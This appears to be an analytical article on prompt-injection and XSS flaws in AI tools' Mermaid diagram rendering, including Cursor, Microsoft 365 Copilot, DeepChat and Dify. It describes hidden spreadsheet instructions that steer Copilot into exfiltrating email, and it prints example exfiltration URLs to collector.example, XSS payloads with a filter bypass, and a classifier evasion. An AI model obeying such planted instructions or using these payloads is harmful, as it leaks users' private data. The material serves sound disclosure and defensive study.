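The severity scores are not evidence that one flaw could leak more data than the other. GitHub rated the first flaw 4.4 and the second 5.9, but the rating rose only because GitHub changed its assumption about privileges. NVD's analysts gave the first flaw 7.5 and did not score the second, so the gap between NVD's 7.5 and GitHub's 5.9 doesn't show that the bypasses were less dangerous.

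### Two labels for one kind of leak

GitHub also classified the two flaws differently under CWE, a public catalogue of software weaknesses. It placed the first in CWE-918, server-side request forgery. In this kind of attack, the attacker usually gets a web server to fetch an address the attacker has chosen, perhaps to reach a machine inside a company's network. Cursor did fetch an address the attacker chose, but the request came from the victim's code editor, and the attacker wanted the data in the request rather than the reply. NVD's analysts recorded that they had too little information to choose a label.

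GitHub classified the second flaw as CWE-200, exposure of sensitive information to an unauthorised actor, and NVD's *CVE-2025-61589 Detail* repeats that classification. The category accurately describes what happens to the user's data, but it is broad enough to cover a stolen laptop or a misaddressed email. A developer couldn't tell from it that they should look at a diagram renderer.

GitHub's descriptions of the two flaws closely match, so their different CWE classes are not evidence that the second flaw worked differently. However, a security team that searches its records by one CWE class will find only one of the flaws.

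Positive Technologies also confusingly lists Mermaid as an affected product alongside Cursor. GitHub named only Cursor in both records and each time listed a new version of Cursor as the fix.

### Has anyone used the flaws?

These records list no real attack that used either flaw. CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, assessed the first flaw on 4 August and the second on 3 October, and entered "none" for exploitation both times. It also judged that attackers could not easily automate the attack.

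CISA's "none" means it knew of no attacks and no public proof of concept. CISA made the entry for the first flaw on the day Rehberger announced his demonstrations, so it went out of date almost at once. For the second flaw, the tracker that counted six Cursor vulnerabilities found no public proof of concept. Shodan's *Vulnerability Details CVE-2025-61589*, from a company that scans the internet for exposed devices, gives the second flaw an EPSS score of 0.001. That is an estimated one-in-a-thousand chance that someone will observe attacks using the flaw in the next 30 days.

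These entries are weak evidence that nobody used the flaws. A victim's editor would have sent a single image request, which looks like ordinary web traffic, and the user would have seen only a diagram. Unless the victim's organisation logged outgoing requests, the clearest trace of the theft would have been in the attacker's server log.

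## How did Microsoft 365 Copilot leak emails through a clickable diagram?

Instructions hidden in a spreadsheet could make Microsoft 365 Copilot search the user's mailbox, put what it found into a web address, and link that address to a diagram that looked like a login button. Clicking the button sent the emails out. Adam Logue, a security researcher, published the attack on 21 October 2025, after Microsoft had disabled links in Copilot's diagrams. Microsoft paid him no reward because its bounty programme did not cover Copilot.

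### A spreadsheet that changes the task

The attack begins when someone receives an Excel file and asks Copilot to summarise it. BeyondMachines' *Microsoft 365 Copilot vulnerability enables data theft through malicious Mermaid diagrams* (2025) describes the file Logue made. Its first sheet held invented business content, such as financial figures, to make the file look ordinary. The sheet also held instructions for Copilot in white text, which it read along with the figures but the user could not see.

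The white text on the first sheet told Copilot to look at the second sheet before summarising. More white text on the second sheet changed the task in stages. It instructed Copilot to drop the summary, collect the user's recent emails, and tell the user that they had to log in to see the document's sensitive information.

Reading a second sheet is a normal part of summarising a spreadsheet, so the first instruction moved Copilot only slightly away from the user's request. Each later instruction built on the one before it. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, Logue arrived at this wording after extensive testing and took the idea from TaskTracker, a Microsoft research project on detecting "task drift". Task drift happens when a model moves away from its user's task towards one it finds in the material it is reading.

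Copilot collected the emails with a tool called `search_enterprise_emails`. The attacker needed no password and no access to the company's tenant (its own area of Microsoft's cloud), because Copilot ran the search on behalf of the user, who could already read the mail. The emails were unrelated to the spreadsheet, and the user had not mentioned email, whereas in Rehberger's test of Cursor the stolen API key was in the same project as the malicious comment.

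### Turning emails into a link

Copilot made a bulleted list of what it had found and converted the list into hexadecimal, a notation in which each byte of data is written as two characters, using the digits 0 to 9 and the letters a to f. In plain English text, each letter, space or punctuation mark takes up one byte, so "M" becomes `4d` and "Meeting" becomes `4d656574696e67`.

Logue's instructions told Copilot to break the result into lines of at most 30 characters, with a backslash at the end of a line to show that the text continued. A made-up email reading "Meeting moved to Friday 3 pm" has 28 characters, so it becomes 56 hexadecimal characters on two lines:

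```
4d656574696e67206d6f7665642074\
6f20467269646179203320706d
```

Each full line holds 15 bytes of the original, so a short email of 300 bytes becomes 600 hexadecimal characters, or 20 lines. An attacker who finds those characters in a server log can quickly join them and convert them back into the email.

Hexadecimal doubles the length of the text, but it suits this attack because none of its 16 characters can break a diagram's syntax or cut a web address short. The quotation marks, brackets and line breaks that fill emails could do both. The ordinary encoding for web addresses would also have dealt with most of these characters, but it leaves words readable, as in `blue%20heron%2042`. A user who glanced at a hexadecimal address would not recognise their own mail in it. Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) at one point wrongly calls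 the data in the link "encrypted", but anyone can decode hexadecimal without a key.

Logue split the data into lines of 30 characters, but his reason is less certain. BeyondMachines writes that Mermaid allows only 200 characters on a line, and Cyber Security News mentions "character limits" without giving a number. The 50,000-character limit in Mermaid 11.0.0 applies to the whole diagram, and a short email is far below it. A limit of 200 characters per line would not explain the choice of 30 either, because 600 characters would then have fitted on three lines. Logue may have wanted a wide margin, or found by trial that Copilot produced working diagrams more often with short lines. Either way, short lines kept the diagram from failing with an error, which would have left the user with no button to click.

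It is also unclear how much mail an attacker could take this way. BeyondMachines mentions the "last 50 corporate emails", but only in a simplified example for general readers, and its account of the attack itself refers to "recent" emails. Fifty 300-byte emails would fill 1,000 lines, and Copilot would have had to write out 30,000 characters without a serious mistake. Fifty 30-byte subject lines would need only 100 lines. It is therefore safer to assume that an attacker could take a few short messages or a list of subject lines than a whole mailbox, although even these could reveal a merger or a dismissal.

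Copilot then wrote the diagram, which used Mermaid's styling and link features to turn a single box into a button with a padlock emoji. The link led to the attacker's server and carried the hexadecimal text. With the made-up email, its address would look like this:

```
https://collector.example/r?d=4d656574696e67206d6f76656420746f20467269646179203320706d
```

In testing, the receiving server could be an instance of Burp Collaborator, a tool that security researchers use to record incoming requests.

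### Did the leak need a click?

Some coverage gave the impression that the emails leaked by themselves. OffSeq's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, an entry on a threat-tracking site, listed the "lack of authentication or user interaction requirements" among the factors that made the flaw more serious. Red Hot Cyber wrote that the data leaked "with a single initial click by the user, without requiring further interaction".

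The user had to click on the diagram, so this was a one-click leak. In *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability*, gnabgib quotes Logue's post, which states that the data went to the attacker's server "when clicked". Further down, Red Hot Cyber's article also describes the user clicking the link and adds that Copilot, unlike Cursor, required user interaction. Cyber Security News also mentions the "initial click" and makes the same comparison with Cursor.

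The "initial click" was probably the click on the fake button. After that click, the attacker needed nothing more from the user. A reader who has just learned that the attack starts with a request for a summary could easily mistake that request for the initial click and conclude that the diagram sent the emails as soon as it appeared.

Once the user asked for the summary, Copilot searched their mailbox and wrote the emails into a link without any further action from the user. Copilot already had access to the mailbox, and the emails were not sent to anyone unless the user clicked the button.

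Logue had to persuade someone to click a link because Copilot's diagrams, unlike Cursor's, did not load images from outside servers. Willison explained this on Hacker News, a forum for programmers (unrelated to the news site The Hacker News), and frontpage has a copy of the discussion.

### What the false login screen added

The attack deceived the user twice, once before the click and once after. Before the click, Copilot displayed a notice that the user had to log in to view the content. This gave the user a reason to click and an explanation for why the summary they had asked for was missing. Office workers see login prompts so often that another is unlikely to surprise them.

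The notice was also more believable than the same words in a stranger's email. A careful person checks who sent a message before following a link in it, and this message came from Copilot, in the user's own Microsoft 365 account, in reply to the user's question.

BeyondMachines reports that after the click, the button turned into an iframe (an embedded page) showing the reply from the attacker's server. Logue had set the server to reply with an image of the screen that Microsoft 365 shows when it redirects someone to log in. The iframe disappeared from the chat after several seconds.

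The false screen's purpose was to stop the user from becoming suspicious. It did not collect any further data, since the server already had the emails when it sent back the image. A user who clicks "Login" and gets an error message or an empty box may wonder what they clicked, and may report it. If a familiar Microsoft screen flashes up and vanishes instead, the user is more likely to think that the login has gone through, or has failed in some ordinary way, and to try again. The button disappeared too, so the user could no longer inspect its address. BeyondMachines warns that this could erase evidence of the attack.

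CyberMaterial's *Copilot flaw exposes sensitive data* also describes the mock login screen, and neither source mentions a stolen password. The screen was a picture, so users couldn't type a password into it. But the iframe displayed whatever the attacker's server returned, so a real attacker might have tried replacing the picture with a working form. If a user had entered a password there, the attacker might have stolen the whole account rather than only some recent emails.

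Microsoft may have used Mermaid's sandbox security level to draw Copilot's diagrams, or built something similar. That level puts each diagram inside an iframe, and a link that opened inside the iframe would replace the diagram with the attacker's page, much as BeyondMachines describes. The sandbox level does not block outside images, though, so Microsoft must have blocked those in some other way.

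### Six weeks from report to repair

Logue sent Microsoft the full attack on 15 August 2025, according to Cyber Security News. He had already discussed it at DEF CON, a hacking conference held each August, with staff of the Microsoft Security Response Center (MSRC), which handles reports of security flaws. MSRC had trouble reproducing the attack at first, so Logue supplied more material, including videos. The team confirmed the flaw on 8 September and resolved it on 26 September. Logue waited almost four more weeks before publishing.

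The attack was probably hard to reproduce because Copilot had to complete five steps: follow the instructions to the second sheet, search the mailbox, encode the result, split it into lines and write a valid diagram. For illustration, if each step worked nine times out of ten, independently of the others, the whole attack would work only 59% of the time (0.9^5). The coverage doesn't include a success rate for the real attack, so it is hard to judge how much a criminal could have relied on it. But someone who sent the same spreadsheet to hundreds of employees would not have needed it to work every time.

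Pistachio, another company, had a worse experience with MSRC that summer. *Copilot broke your audit log* describes a flaw, found on 4 July, that let Copilot open a file without recording the access in the log companies use to check who has read what. Pistachio reported the flaw at once, and complains that Microsoft did not follow its own published guide to handling such reports. Logue's case moved slowly at first, but Microsoft confirmed the flaw and fixed it before publication.

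Microsoft fixed the leak by removing working links from Copilot's diagrams. Copilot could still draw diagrams, but clicking the padlock button would now do nothing. daily.dev's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Arbitrary Data Exfiltration Via Mermaid Diagrams* describes the change slightly more broadly, as removing the ability to interact with any dynamic content in a diagram.

Removing the links closes the route that Logue used, and users lose little, since few need to click on a flowchart in a chat window. BeyondMachines doubts that the repair covers every way of exploiting the flaw, but gives no example of an attack that still works. The doubt is reasonable, because the repair to Cursor had left other ways to exploit its flaw. But Microsoft's task was simpler than Anysphere's. Anysphere had to stop every kind of diagram text that could fetch an image, whereas Copilot already blocked outside images,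 so Microsoft only had to remove the links.

The repair did not stop Copilot from following instructions in a spreadsheet. In the discussion that frontpage copied, the commenter luke-stanley argued that Mermaid was a side issue, because an ordinary link might have leaked the data too, and that Microsoft should address the assistant's tendency to follow unrelated instructions. Willison defended blocking the route by which data could leave, because nobody can yet fix that tendency in current models. Another commenter, MattPalmer1086, accepted that Microsoft had no other option that kept the product useful, but did not think this made it the right one. Luke-stanley also pointed out that a program made only for summarising does not need to follow instructions in a document, and that such programs exist. That is a fair point about summaries, but Microsoft sells Copilot as an assistant that can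 also search mail and draft documents, and those tasks require a model that can follow instructions.

An ordinary link might not have worked as well as luke-stanley supposed. In spring 2025, Microsoft announced extra protection against malicious links in Copilot Chat's answers. It planned to finish the rollout by late May and later extend the protection to Copilot Chat in the Office apps. The link in Logue's diagram still reached his server in August. The protection may not have covered diagrams or the version of Copilot he tested, or it may have covered both but failed to recognise a newly created address as malicious.

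### No bounty and no known CVE

Microsoft runs a bounty programme, which pays people who report security flaws privately. MSRC had already accepted that the flaw Logue reported was real, but the bounty team told him that Microsoft 365 Copilot was outside the programme's scope.

Microsoft's refusal to pay a bounty drew more anger in the Hacker News discussion than the flaw did. One commenter wrote that it would discourage researchers from looking for flaws in Copilot and reporting them responsibly. Another said Microsoft was in effect telling people to sell such discoveries instead. A third asked whether any company pays bounties on all its products. Someone replied that Microsoft promotes Copilot above all its other products, so leaving it out is harder to excuse than leaving out Visio, its diagramming program. The critics have the better argument, because Copilot can search a company's email,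 and a flaw that exposes that email is worth money to criminals whether or not Microsoft pays for it.

According to daily.dev, the product was out of scope "at the time". The rules may have changed later, but daily.dev does not mention a change.

daily.dev, BeyondMachines, Cyber Security News and Red Hot Cyber don't give a CVE number for the flaw either. Microsoft may have issued one that the coverage missed, but it more likely issued none. It has given CVE numbers to other Copilot leaks. Willison's *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* gives CVE-2025-32711 for EchoLeak, the earlier attack by email. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* covers several flaws that Rehberger reported in 2025, which received CVE-2026-24299. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) is the record for another leak, CVE-2026-42824, published on 4 June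 2026.

Because the flaw has no CVE, a security team that tracks flaws by CVE number could miss it. That matters less than it would have for Cursor, whose users had to install a new version to be safe. Copilot runs largely on Microsoft's own servers, so Microsoft could change how it displayed diagrams without users having to do anything. But a company that wanted to know whether its employees had clicked such a button between August and September would have had no official record of the flaw to start from.

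Without a CVE, the Copilot flaw also has no official CVSS score to compare with Cursor's. OffSeq reports a rating of "medium", which covers scores from 4.0 to 6.9, and the published formula also gives a score in that range. Using NVD's assumptions for the first Cursor flaw, but counting the user's click, would give 6.5. Also treating the attack as highly complex, as GitHub did with Cursor, would lower the score to 5.3.

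## What did diagram renderers in other AI products allow?

A Mermaid diagram could run an attacker's script in at least four other AI products: DeepChat, LobeChat, Dify and Open WebUI. In DeepChat and LobeChat, which run as desktop programs, the script could then run commands on the user's computer. Microsoft also fixed Visual Studio, its programming environment, under the same CVE number as the first Cursor flaw, and described the problem as data exfiltration.

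### Scripts as well as images

The attacks on Cursor and Copilot relied on the assistant to find the secret and write it into an address. An attacker who can run a script in the chat window needs much less help from the assistant, because the script can read the conversation from the page and send it out in its own request. In a web application, the script can usually also act as the logged-in user, for example by opening older chats.

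The CVE descriptions for these four products report that scripts ran and, for the two desktop programs, that this could lead to command execution. They don't mention stolen conversations or keys. Such a script could steal data, but that is an inference from what scripts can do. Rehberger and Logue, by contrast, showed private data arriving at a server.

Some of the attacks don't need prompt injection. Several of the records describe stored XSS, in which an application saves an attacker's text and the script in it runs when someone later displays it. A person could put a malicious diagram into a file or a chat message without involving a model. Prompt injection could also deliver the diagram, because an assistant that has read a hostile web page could write it.

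### DeepChat's repeated repairs

DeepChat is an open-source desktop program for chatting with AI models and running agents. Between 9 September and 16 December 2025, GitHub published four CVE records for flaws in how it drew Mermaid diagrams.

The attack on DeepChat first used links. OSV's *CVE-2025-55733* (2025) describes how any website could include a specially made `deepchat:` link that ran commands on a visitor's computer after one click. DeepChat's developers fixed this in version 0.3.1.

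Three weeks after GitHub published that flaw, it published the first one involving diagrams, CVE-2025-58768. DeepChat's Mermaid component used `innerHTML` to put user content directly into the page, so a diagram could carry a script. OSV's *DeepChat's Mermaid rendering has XSS leading to RCE* (2025) attributes the flaw to the developers' incomplete fix for the earlier script flaw. The attack was the same except that it began with a diagram instead of a link. The developers released another fix in version 0.3.5.

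A script in an ordinary web page can't start programs, because the browser isolates pages from the rest of the computer. DeepChat, however, uses Electron, a framework for making desktop programs out of web pages. An Electron program shows a web page in its window, while a main process in the background can open files and start other programs. The page and the main process exchange messages over a channel called inter-process communication (IPC). Developers can restrict the page to a few harmless requests, but DeepChat exposed the channel to any script in the page. Stefani (2025), in *DeepChat AI agent XSS-to-RCE via Mermaid and Electron IPC*, treats this exposure as a separate weakness from the unsafe diagrams and notes that the techniques for exploiting each were already well understood.

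According to GCVE's *CVE-2025-66222* (2025), the script could run a command by registering a malicious MCP server and then starting it. Many MCP servers run on the user's own machine, and the user adds one by giving the application a command that starts it. DeepChat needed this feature for its agents, but a script that could reach it through IPC could supply any command the attacker chose.

GitHub published this record on 3 December. The description covers "0.5.0 and earlier", but the field that security software reads lists only versions below 0.5.0. Until NVD's analysts included 0.5.0, a company that relied on an automatic check could have concluded that 0.5.0 was safe.

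DeepChat's developers responded with a filter that was supposed to strip dangerous attributes from the diagram's HTML. They probably released it in version 0.5.1, since the flaw published on 3 December affected 0.5.0 and the next one affected 0.5.1. The filter used regular expressions, which are patterns for finding particular sequences of characters. MITRE's *DeepChat's Incomplete XSS Fix Allows RCE through Mermaid Content* (2025), the record for CVE-2025-66481, explains that an attacker could get past it by leaving out quotation marks and encoding some characters. A simplified example, which is not taken from DeepChat's code, shows the difficulty:

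```
<img src="x" onerror="alert(1)">
<img src=x onerror=&#97;lert(1)>
```

A browser treats these two lines the same way. HTML allows an attribute without quotation marks, and `&#97;` is another way to write the letter "a". The browser decodes it before running the script. A filter that looks for `onerror="` or the word "alert" would catch the first line and miss the second. Adding patterns helps only until someone finds another spelling that browsers accept.

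GitHub published this bypass on 9 December, when no fix existed. NVD's *CVE-2025-66481 Detail* repeats that no fix was available, so a reader who looks up only that number won't learn which version to install. The version to install is probably 0.5.3, which GitHub named a week later in the record for CVE-2025-67744. That record covers every earlier version.

GCVE's *CVE-2025-67744* (2025) lists two causes for this last flaw, an "unsafe Mermaid configuration" and the exposed IPC interface. GitHub doesn't say in the record whether version 0.5.3 fixed both. If the developers changed only the Mermaid settings, another script flaw anywhere in DeepChat could again let an attacker run commands.

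A similar filter failed in May 2026 in DeepChat's code for displaying SVG images. OSV's *CVE-2026-43900* (2026) describes a check that searched the text for `javascript:` and missed it when an attacker encoded the characters. The developers fixed the flaw in version 1.0.4-beta.1.

Cursor also needed a second patch after researchers got around the first, but DeepChat's history is more informative because GitHub described the gaps. The August link attack and all four Mermaid flaws involved the exposed IPC channel. If the developers had closed it in August, diagrams could still have run scripts, but only inside the chat window. Instead, they spent several releases blocking individual ways for a script to get in.

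GitHub scored the three December flaws 9.7. NVD analysed two of them and, using the same assumptions, scored them 9.6. The published formula also gives 9.6 (9.5936 rounded up), so GitHub's figure is probably a miscalculation. These scores are far above Cursor's because an attacker who can run commands can also alter files and stop programs, which an image request can't do. CISA noted a public proof of concept for each December flaw but recorded no real attacks in its entries.

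### The same combination in LobeChat

In January 2026, GitHub disclosed a nearly identical flaw in LobeChat, another open-source chat application. GCVE's *CVE-2026-23733* (2026) describes a diagram that could run a script, which could then run system commands through an exposed channel called `electronAPI`.

The flaw was in LobeChat's code for artifacts, items such as diagrams that the application displays separately from the text of an answer. Kodem's *CVE-2026-23733* reproduces the line responsible:

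```
return <Mermaid variant={'borderless'}>{content}</Mermaid>;
```

Here `content` is the diagram text, which may come from the user's messages or the model's. LobeChat passed it to the Mermaid component without sanitizing it. The code handled a diagram the user had typed the same way as one an assistant had written after reading a stranger's document.

LobeChat's developers fixed the flaw in version 2.0.0-next.180, a pre-release of version 2. On npm, a service that distributes JavaScript code, every version of LobeChat's package up to 1.143.2 was vulnerable, and Kodem lists no fixed version.

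GitHub again published two severity scores. Wiz's *CVE-2026-23733* explains that GitHub's advisory database lists 9.6, which assumes an attacker can act over a network without any privileges, while GitHub's CVE record lists 6.4 because it treats the attack as local. In CVSS, "local" can mean that the attacker already has access to the machine or has to get its user to open something. The higher score is easier to defend for a chat application that displays text written by a model, since an attacker can influence that text remotely. GitHub treated DeepChat's flaws, which worked in almost the same way, as network attacks.

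### Dify, Open WebUI and the loose level

Dify and Open WebUI had both set Mermaid to its "loose" security level, which allows HTML and clicks in diagrams. Both products are web applications, so a script from a diagram ran in the user's browser and had no Electron channel to the rest of the computer.

Dify rendered Mermaid diagrams at the `loose` security level by default. OSV's *CVE-2026-21866* (2026) describes a stored XSS flaw in chats that affected every Dify version before 1.11.2. This appears to be the flaw that Snyk's `javascript:` link exploited. Dify's switch to `strict` removed the setting that had let the script through, but Dify still depended on Mermaid's own sanitization, which had failed at the `strict` level in some earlier Mermaid versions.

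INCIBE's *CVE-2026-21866* (2026) lists two scores for Dify, 5.1 and 5.4. They come from different versions of CVSS, and both count as medium.

Open WebUI, a self-hosted platform for using AI models, had a flaw in its file preview panel. If a Markdown file contained a Mermaid diagram, the panel rendered it at the `loose` security level and inserted the resulting SVG into the page with `innerHTML`. A user who previewed a hostile file would run the attacker's script even without asking the assistant about the file, so the attack needed no prompt injection.

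Applications commonly use `innerHTML` to insert Mermaid's drawing into the page, but Mermaid 11.0.0 skips its final DOMPurify pass when its security level is set to `loose`. An application that inserts the drawing unchanged may therefore put the attacker's text into the page unsanitised.

Corgea's *Open WebUI* reports that the attack worked on version 0.8.12. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54011* (2026) lists every version before 0.9.6 as affected and 0.9.6 as fixed.

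NVD's *CVE-2026-54011 Detail* (2026) describes Open WebUI as "designed to operate entirely offline". Offline operation can keep a company's questions away from an outside AI provider, but it doesn't by itself prevent this kind of attack from leaking data, because the script runs in an employee's browser and can reach the internet if the employee's computer can.

GitLab gives the flaw a score of 8.7 (high), but Secualive's *CVE-2026-54011* (2026) gives it 5.4 (medium). GitLab's score is for an attacker with an ordinary account, a victim who has to do something such as open the preview, and a script that can read and change a great deal. Rating the script's ability to read and change data as low instead of high produces exactly 5.4, which is also Dify's score. The higher score suits an installation where people discuss confidential work or where an administrator might open the file, while the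 lower one could suit a test server with nothing valuable on it.

The CVE descriptions don't explain why either product's developers chose the loose setting, so the reasons given here are guesses. The developers may have wanted clickable nodes or, like the Joplin user, HTML images in diagrams. Or they may have copied the setting from an example, or chosen it while they controlled the diagram text and not reconsidered when models began writing it.

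### What Microsoft repaired in Visual Studio

Microsoft released Visual Studio 2022 version 17.14.17 on 14 October 2025. Its *Visual Studio release notes* list CVE-2025-54132, "Arbitrary Data Exfiltration Via Markdown Mermaid", among the flaws fixed in that version. Microsoft also published a separate security notice, which the vulnerability tracker exploitDog reproduces. Most of the notice is GitHub's description of the Cursor flaw, but Microsoft added that its Visual Studio updates "incorporate updates in Mermaid which address this vulnerability".

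The notice lists Visual Studio 2022 version 17.14 as the affected product but doesn't give the first vulnerable release. Microsoft announced the built-in diagram feature on 11 September in *Generating and Viewing Mermaid Diagrams with Copilot* (2025); before that, users needed an extension. The flaw can't be older than this feature, so the vulnerable releases were probably the versions of 17.14 before 17.14.17 that could draw diagrams. Tenable's *Security Updates for Microsoft Visual Studio Products 17.14.17 (October 2025)* (2025) also lists 17.14.17 as the fix. Tenable's "high" rating covers the whole update, which fixed several other flaws, while Microsoft's notice rates this one 4.4, the score GitHub had given the Cursor flaw.

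Microsoft's accounts of the feature differ on whether the user has to click to see the diagram. In the September announcement, Copilot writes the diagram text in the chat, and the user clicks a Preview button to open the diagram in the Markdown editor. In the release notes, Visual Studio draws the diagram in the chat window automatically. A diagram that loaded an outside image would leak data after one click in the first version and with no click in the second. Microsoft may have changed the feature between the two accounts, or one of them may be imprecise. The words "Markdown Mermaid" suggest the editor's preview but don't rule out the chat, where assistants also write in Markdown.

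In either case, a stranger's Markdown file could leak a secret only if Copilot found the secret and wrote it into the diagram, as in Cursor.

The phrase "updates in Mermaid" could mislead other developers because it might refer to a newer version of the Mermaid library or to Visual Studio's own diagram code. Microsoft names no library version. GitHub attributed the original flaw to Cursor rather than to Mermaid, so Microsoft's notice is weak evidence that updating the library alone would stop outside images from loading.

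GitHub published the bypasses of Cursor's first patch eleven days before Microsoft's update. Microsoft lists no fix for that second flaw, CVE-2025-61589, in its notes for the update or for later 17.14 releases up to April 2026. Its October fix may already have covered the bypasses, but the notes don't show whether it did.

### The products compared

| Product and flaw | Trigger | Reported effect | Repair |
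|---|---|---|---|
| DeepChat, CVE-2025-58768 | Displaying a diagram with hostile content | Script, then commands on the computer | Version 0.3.5 |
| DeepChat, CVE-2025-66222 | Displaying a hostile diagram | Script, then commands through a malicious MCP server | Attribute filter, probably in 0.5.1 |
| DeepChat, CVE-2025-66481 | Displaying a diagram written to get past that filter | Script, then commands | None at publication; probably 0.5.3 |
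| DeepChat, CVE-2025-67744 | Displaying a hostile diagram under unsafe Mermaid settings | Script, then commands | Version 0.5.3 |
| LobeChat, CVE-2026-23733 | Displaying a hostile Mermaid artifact | Script, then commands through `electronAPI` | Version 2.0.0-next.180 |
| Dify, CVE-2026-21866 | Clicking a node in a chat diagram, in Snyk's attack | Script in the browser | Strict level; version 1.11.2 |
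| Open WebUI, CVE-2026-54011 | Previewing a hostile Markdown file | Script in the browser | Version 0.9.6 |
| Visual Studio 2022, CVE-2025-54132 | Drawing a diagram that contains an outside image | Private data sent in the image request | Version 17.14.17 |

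## Why were diagram renderers missed when images were being blocked?

Vendors mostly blocked particular ways of writing an image or a link, and Mermaid has its own notation for both. That is the best-supported explanation for Microsoft 365 Copilot, where Microsoft had blocked outside images and links in ordinary answers before Logue reported the diagram leak. The explanation for Cursor is less clear, because its chat had been drawing diagrams for less than four weeks when Rehberger reported the leak, and Anysphere may never have blocked ordinary images there. Neither company appears to have said publicly why it missed the diagrams, so any explanation rests largely on dates, code and how the products behaved.

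### How vendors blocked images, 2023 to 2025

Microsoft was the first vendor to fix the Markdown image leak, Rehberger recalls on Embrace The Red. He reported it in Bing Chat on 8 April 2023, and on 15 June Microsoft told him it had a fix. When he repeated his attacks, they failed. In a post there at the time, he credited this at least partly to a new content security policy, which tells the browser which servers a page may load images, scripts and other resources from. Bing Chat's policy listed four Bing domains. The model could still write an image address containing a secret, but the browser would no longer request the image.

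Rehberger reported the leak in Claude on 12 July 2023, and Anthropic closed the report two weeks later. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* describes the apparent fix. Claude's chat window stopped loading images automatically and displayed a "Show Image" button instead, so the leak now required one click from the user rather than none.

OpenAI also received a report in April 2023 and at first marked it "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*. In December, ChatGPT's web application began sending each image's address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe` before displaying it. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, found this "a bit weird", because OpenAI could simply have blocked images from outside domains. Rehberger tested 36 addresses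 on his own server, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed the check. He used them to leak the word "hi", one letter at a time. The iPhone app did not have the check yet, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*.

GitHub fixed Copilot Chat, its programming assistant, in June 2024, less than four months after Rehberger's report. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* suggests that the assistant stopped displaying Markdown images. Willison (2024), in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, describes a narrower change that disabled images from untrusted domains. Either change would have stopped the attack, but some version of Copilot Chat evidently still displayed images, because a researcher found another image leak there in June 2025. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains that this second attack got around GitHub's content security policy by using GitHub's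 own infrastructure. GitHub then turned off images in Copilot Chat completely.

Links were also a known way to leak data by this time. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes a 2024 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot in which the assistant read the victim's emails and hid data from them in a link using invisible characters.

### EchoLeak and Microsoft's defences

Before the diagram report, Microsoft 365 Copilot already had three defences that EchoLeak, the attack that began with an email, had to get past. Aim Labs, Aim Security's research team, reported the attack in January 2025. Microsoft deployed the fix in May, and both published details on 11 June. Ravia (2025) describes each defence in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*.

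A classifier checked incoming text for hidden instructions. The researchers got past it by wording the email as if its instructions were for the employee who received it, and by never mentioning Copilot or AI.

The next defence was a filter that removed outside links and images from Copilot's answers. Markdown, however, has more than one way to write an image:

```
![logo](https://collector.example/dot.png?d=blue%20heron%2042)

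![logo][ref]
[ref]: https://collector.example/dot.png?d=blue%20heron%2042
```

Both forms display the same picture. Copilot's filter removed the first and left the second, in which the address is on a separate line.

The browser's content security policy still blocked the request because the attacker's server was not on its list of allowed sites. But the list had more than two dozen entries, including one that covered Microsoft Teams, and a Teams service would fetch any address included in a request to it. The browser therefore requested the image from Teams, which requested it from the attacker's server and passed on the secret. The researchers had first found a SharePoint address that worked in much the same way, but only if the user accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

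Goldman (2025) reported in Fortune that EchoLeak was the first known zero-click attack on an AI agent. Rehberger's attack on Bing Chat two years earlier was also zero-click by the usual meaning of the term. According to Ravia, earlier victims had to direct the assistant to the hostile page or file, while an EchoLeak victim only had to ask Copilot about their own work.

Allowed domains also led to data leaks in other products in 2025. Salesforce's policy for Agentforce, its assistant for sales and service staff, still allowed a domain whose registration had expired. Researchers registered the domain and received customer data there, according to Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*. Superhuman's leak through Google Forms also depended on an allowed domain.

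Microsoft described these defences in July 2025. It separates probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to work, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail. It classes its response to Rehberger's image report as deterministic. Microsoft also says it looks beyond each report to "the general class of issues, including variants", and cites blocking certain untrusted links as an example. Logue reported his diagram attack to Microsoft on 15 August.

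### Which products had blocked ordinary images?

Several AI products had not blocked ordinary images in 2025, so an attacker did not need a diagram. Windsurf, another AI code editor, is the closest comparison with Cursor. Rehberger reported two leaks in Windsurf on 30 May 2025, one through a tool that reads web pages and one through ordinary images. Windsurf acknowledged the report but did not answer his later questions. After three months, he published *Hijacking Windsurf* on Embrace The Red, leaving out the exact instructions because the leaks still worked.

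Continue, an AI extension for the code editor Visual Studio Code, had the same weakness. A comment in a source file could make the assistant read the project's `.env` file, which often holds passwords and keys, and send the contents out in an image address. The security company VerSprite reported this on 20 August 2025. The next day, Continue's developers released a fix that asks the user before loading an outside image, according to VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue*.

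In December 2025, the researcher veganmosfet built a Dify chatbot that answered questions from two PDF files. Hidden text in one of them told the chatbot to add an image, whose address contained the user's name, to any answer about "prompt engineering". The name reached an outside server. *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend* explains that Dify set no content security policy for such images by default. Dify's diagrams could also run scripts in versions before 1.11.2, so it had security gaps in both images and diagrams. PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* describes another leak through ordinary images, in the chat application HuggingChat. PromptArmor reported it on 1 December 2025 and published after getting no response.

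In Microsoft 365 Copilot, by contrast, diagrams were left out of an existing defence. Ravia's tests show that Microsoft was filtering both images and links out of Copilot's answers months before Logue's report, although the filter had gaps.

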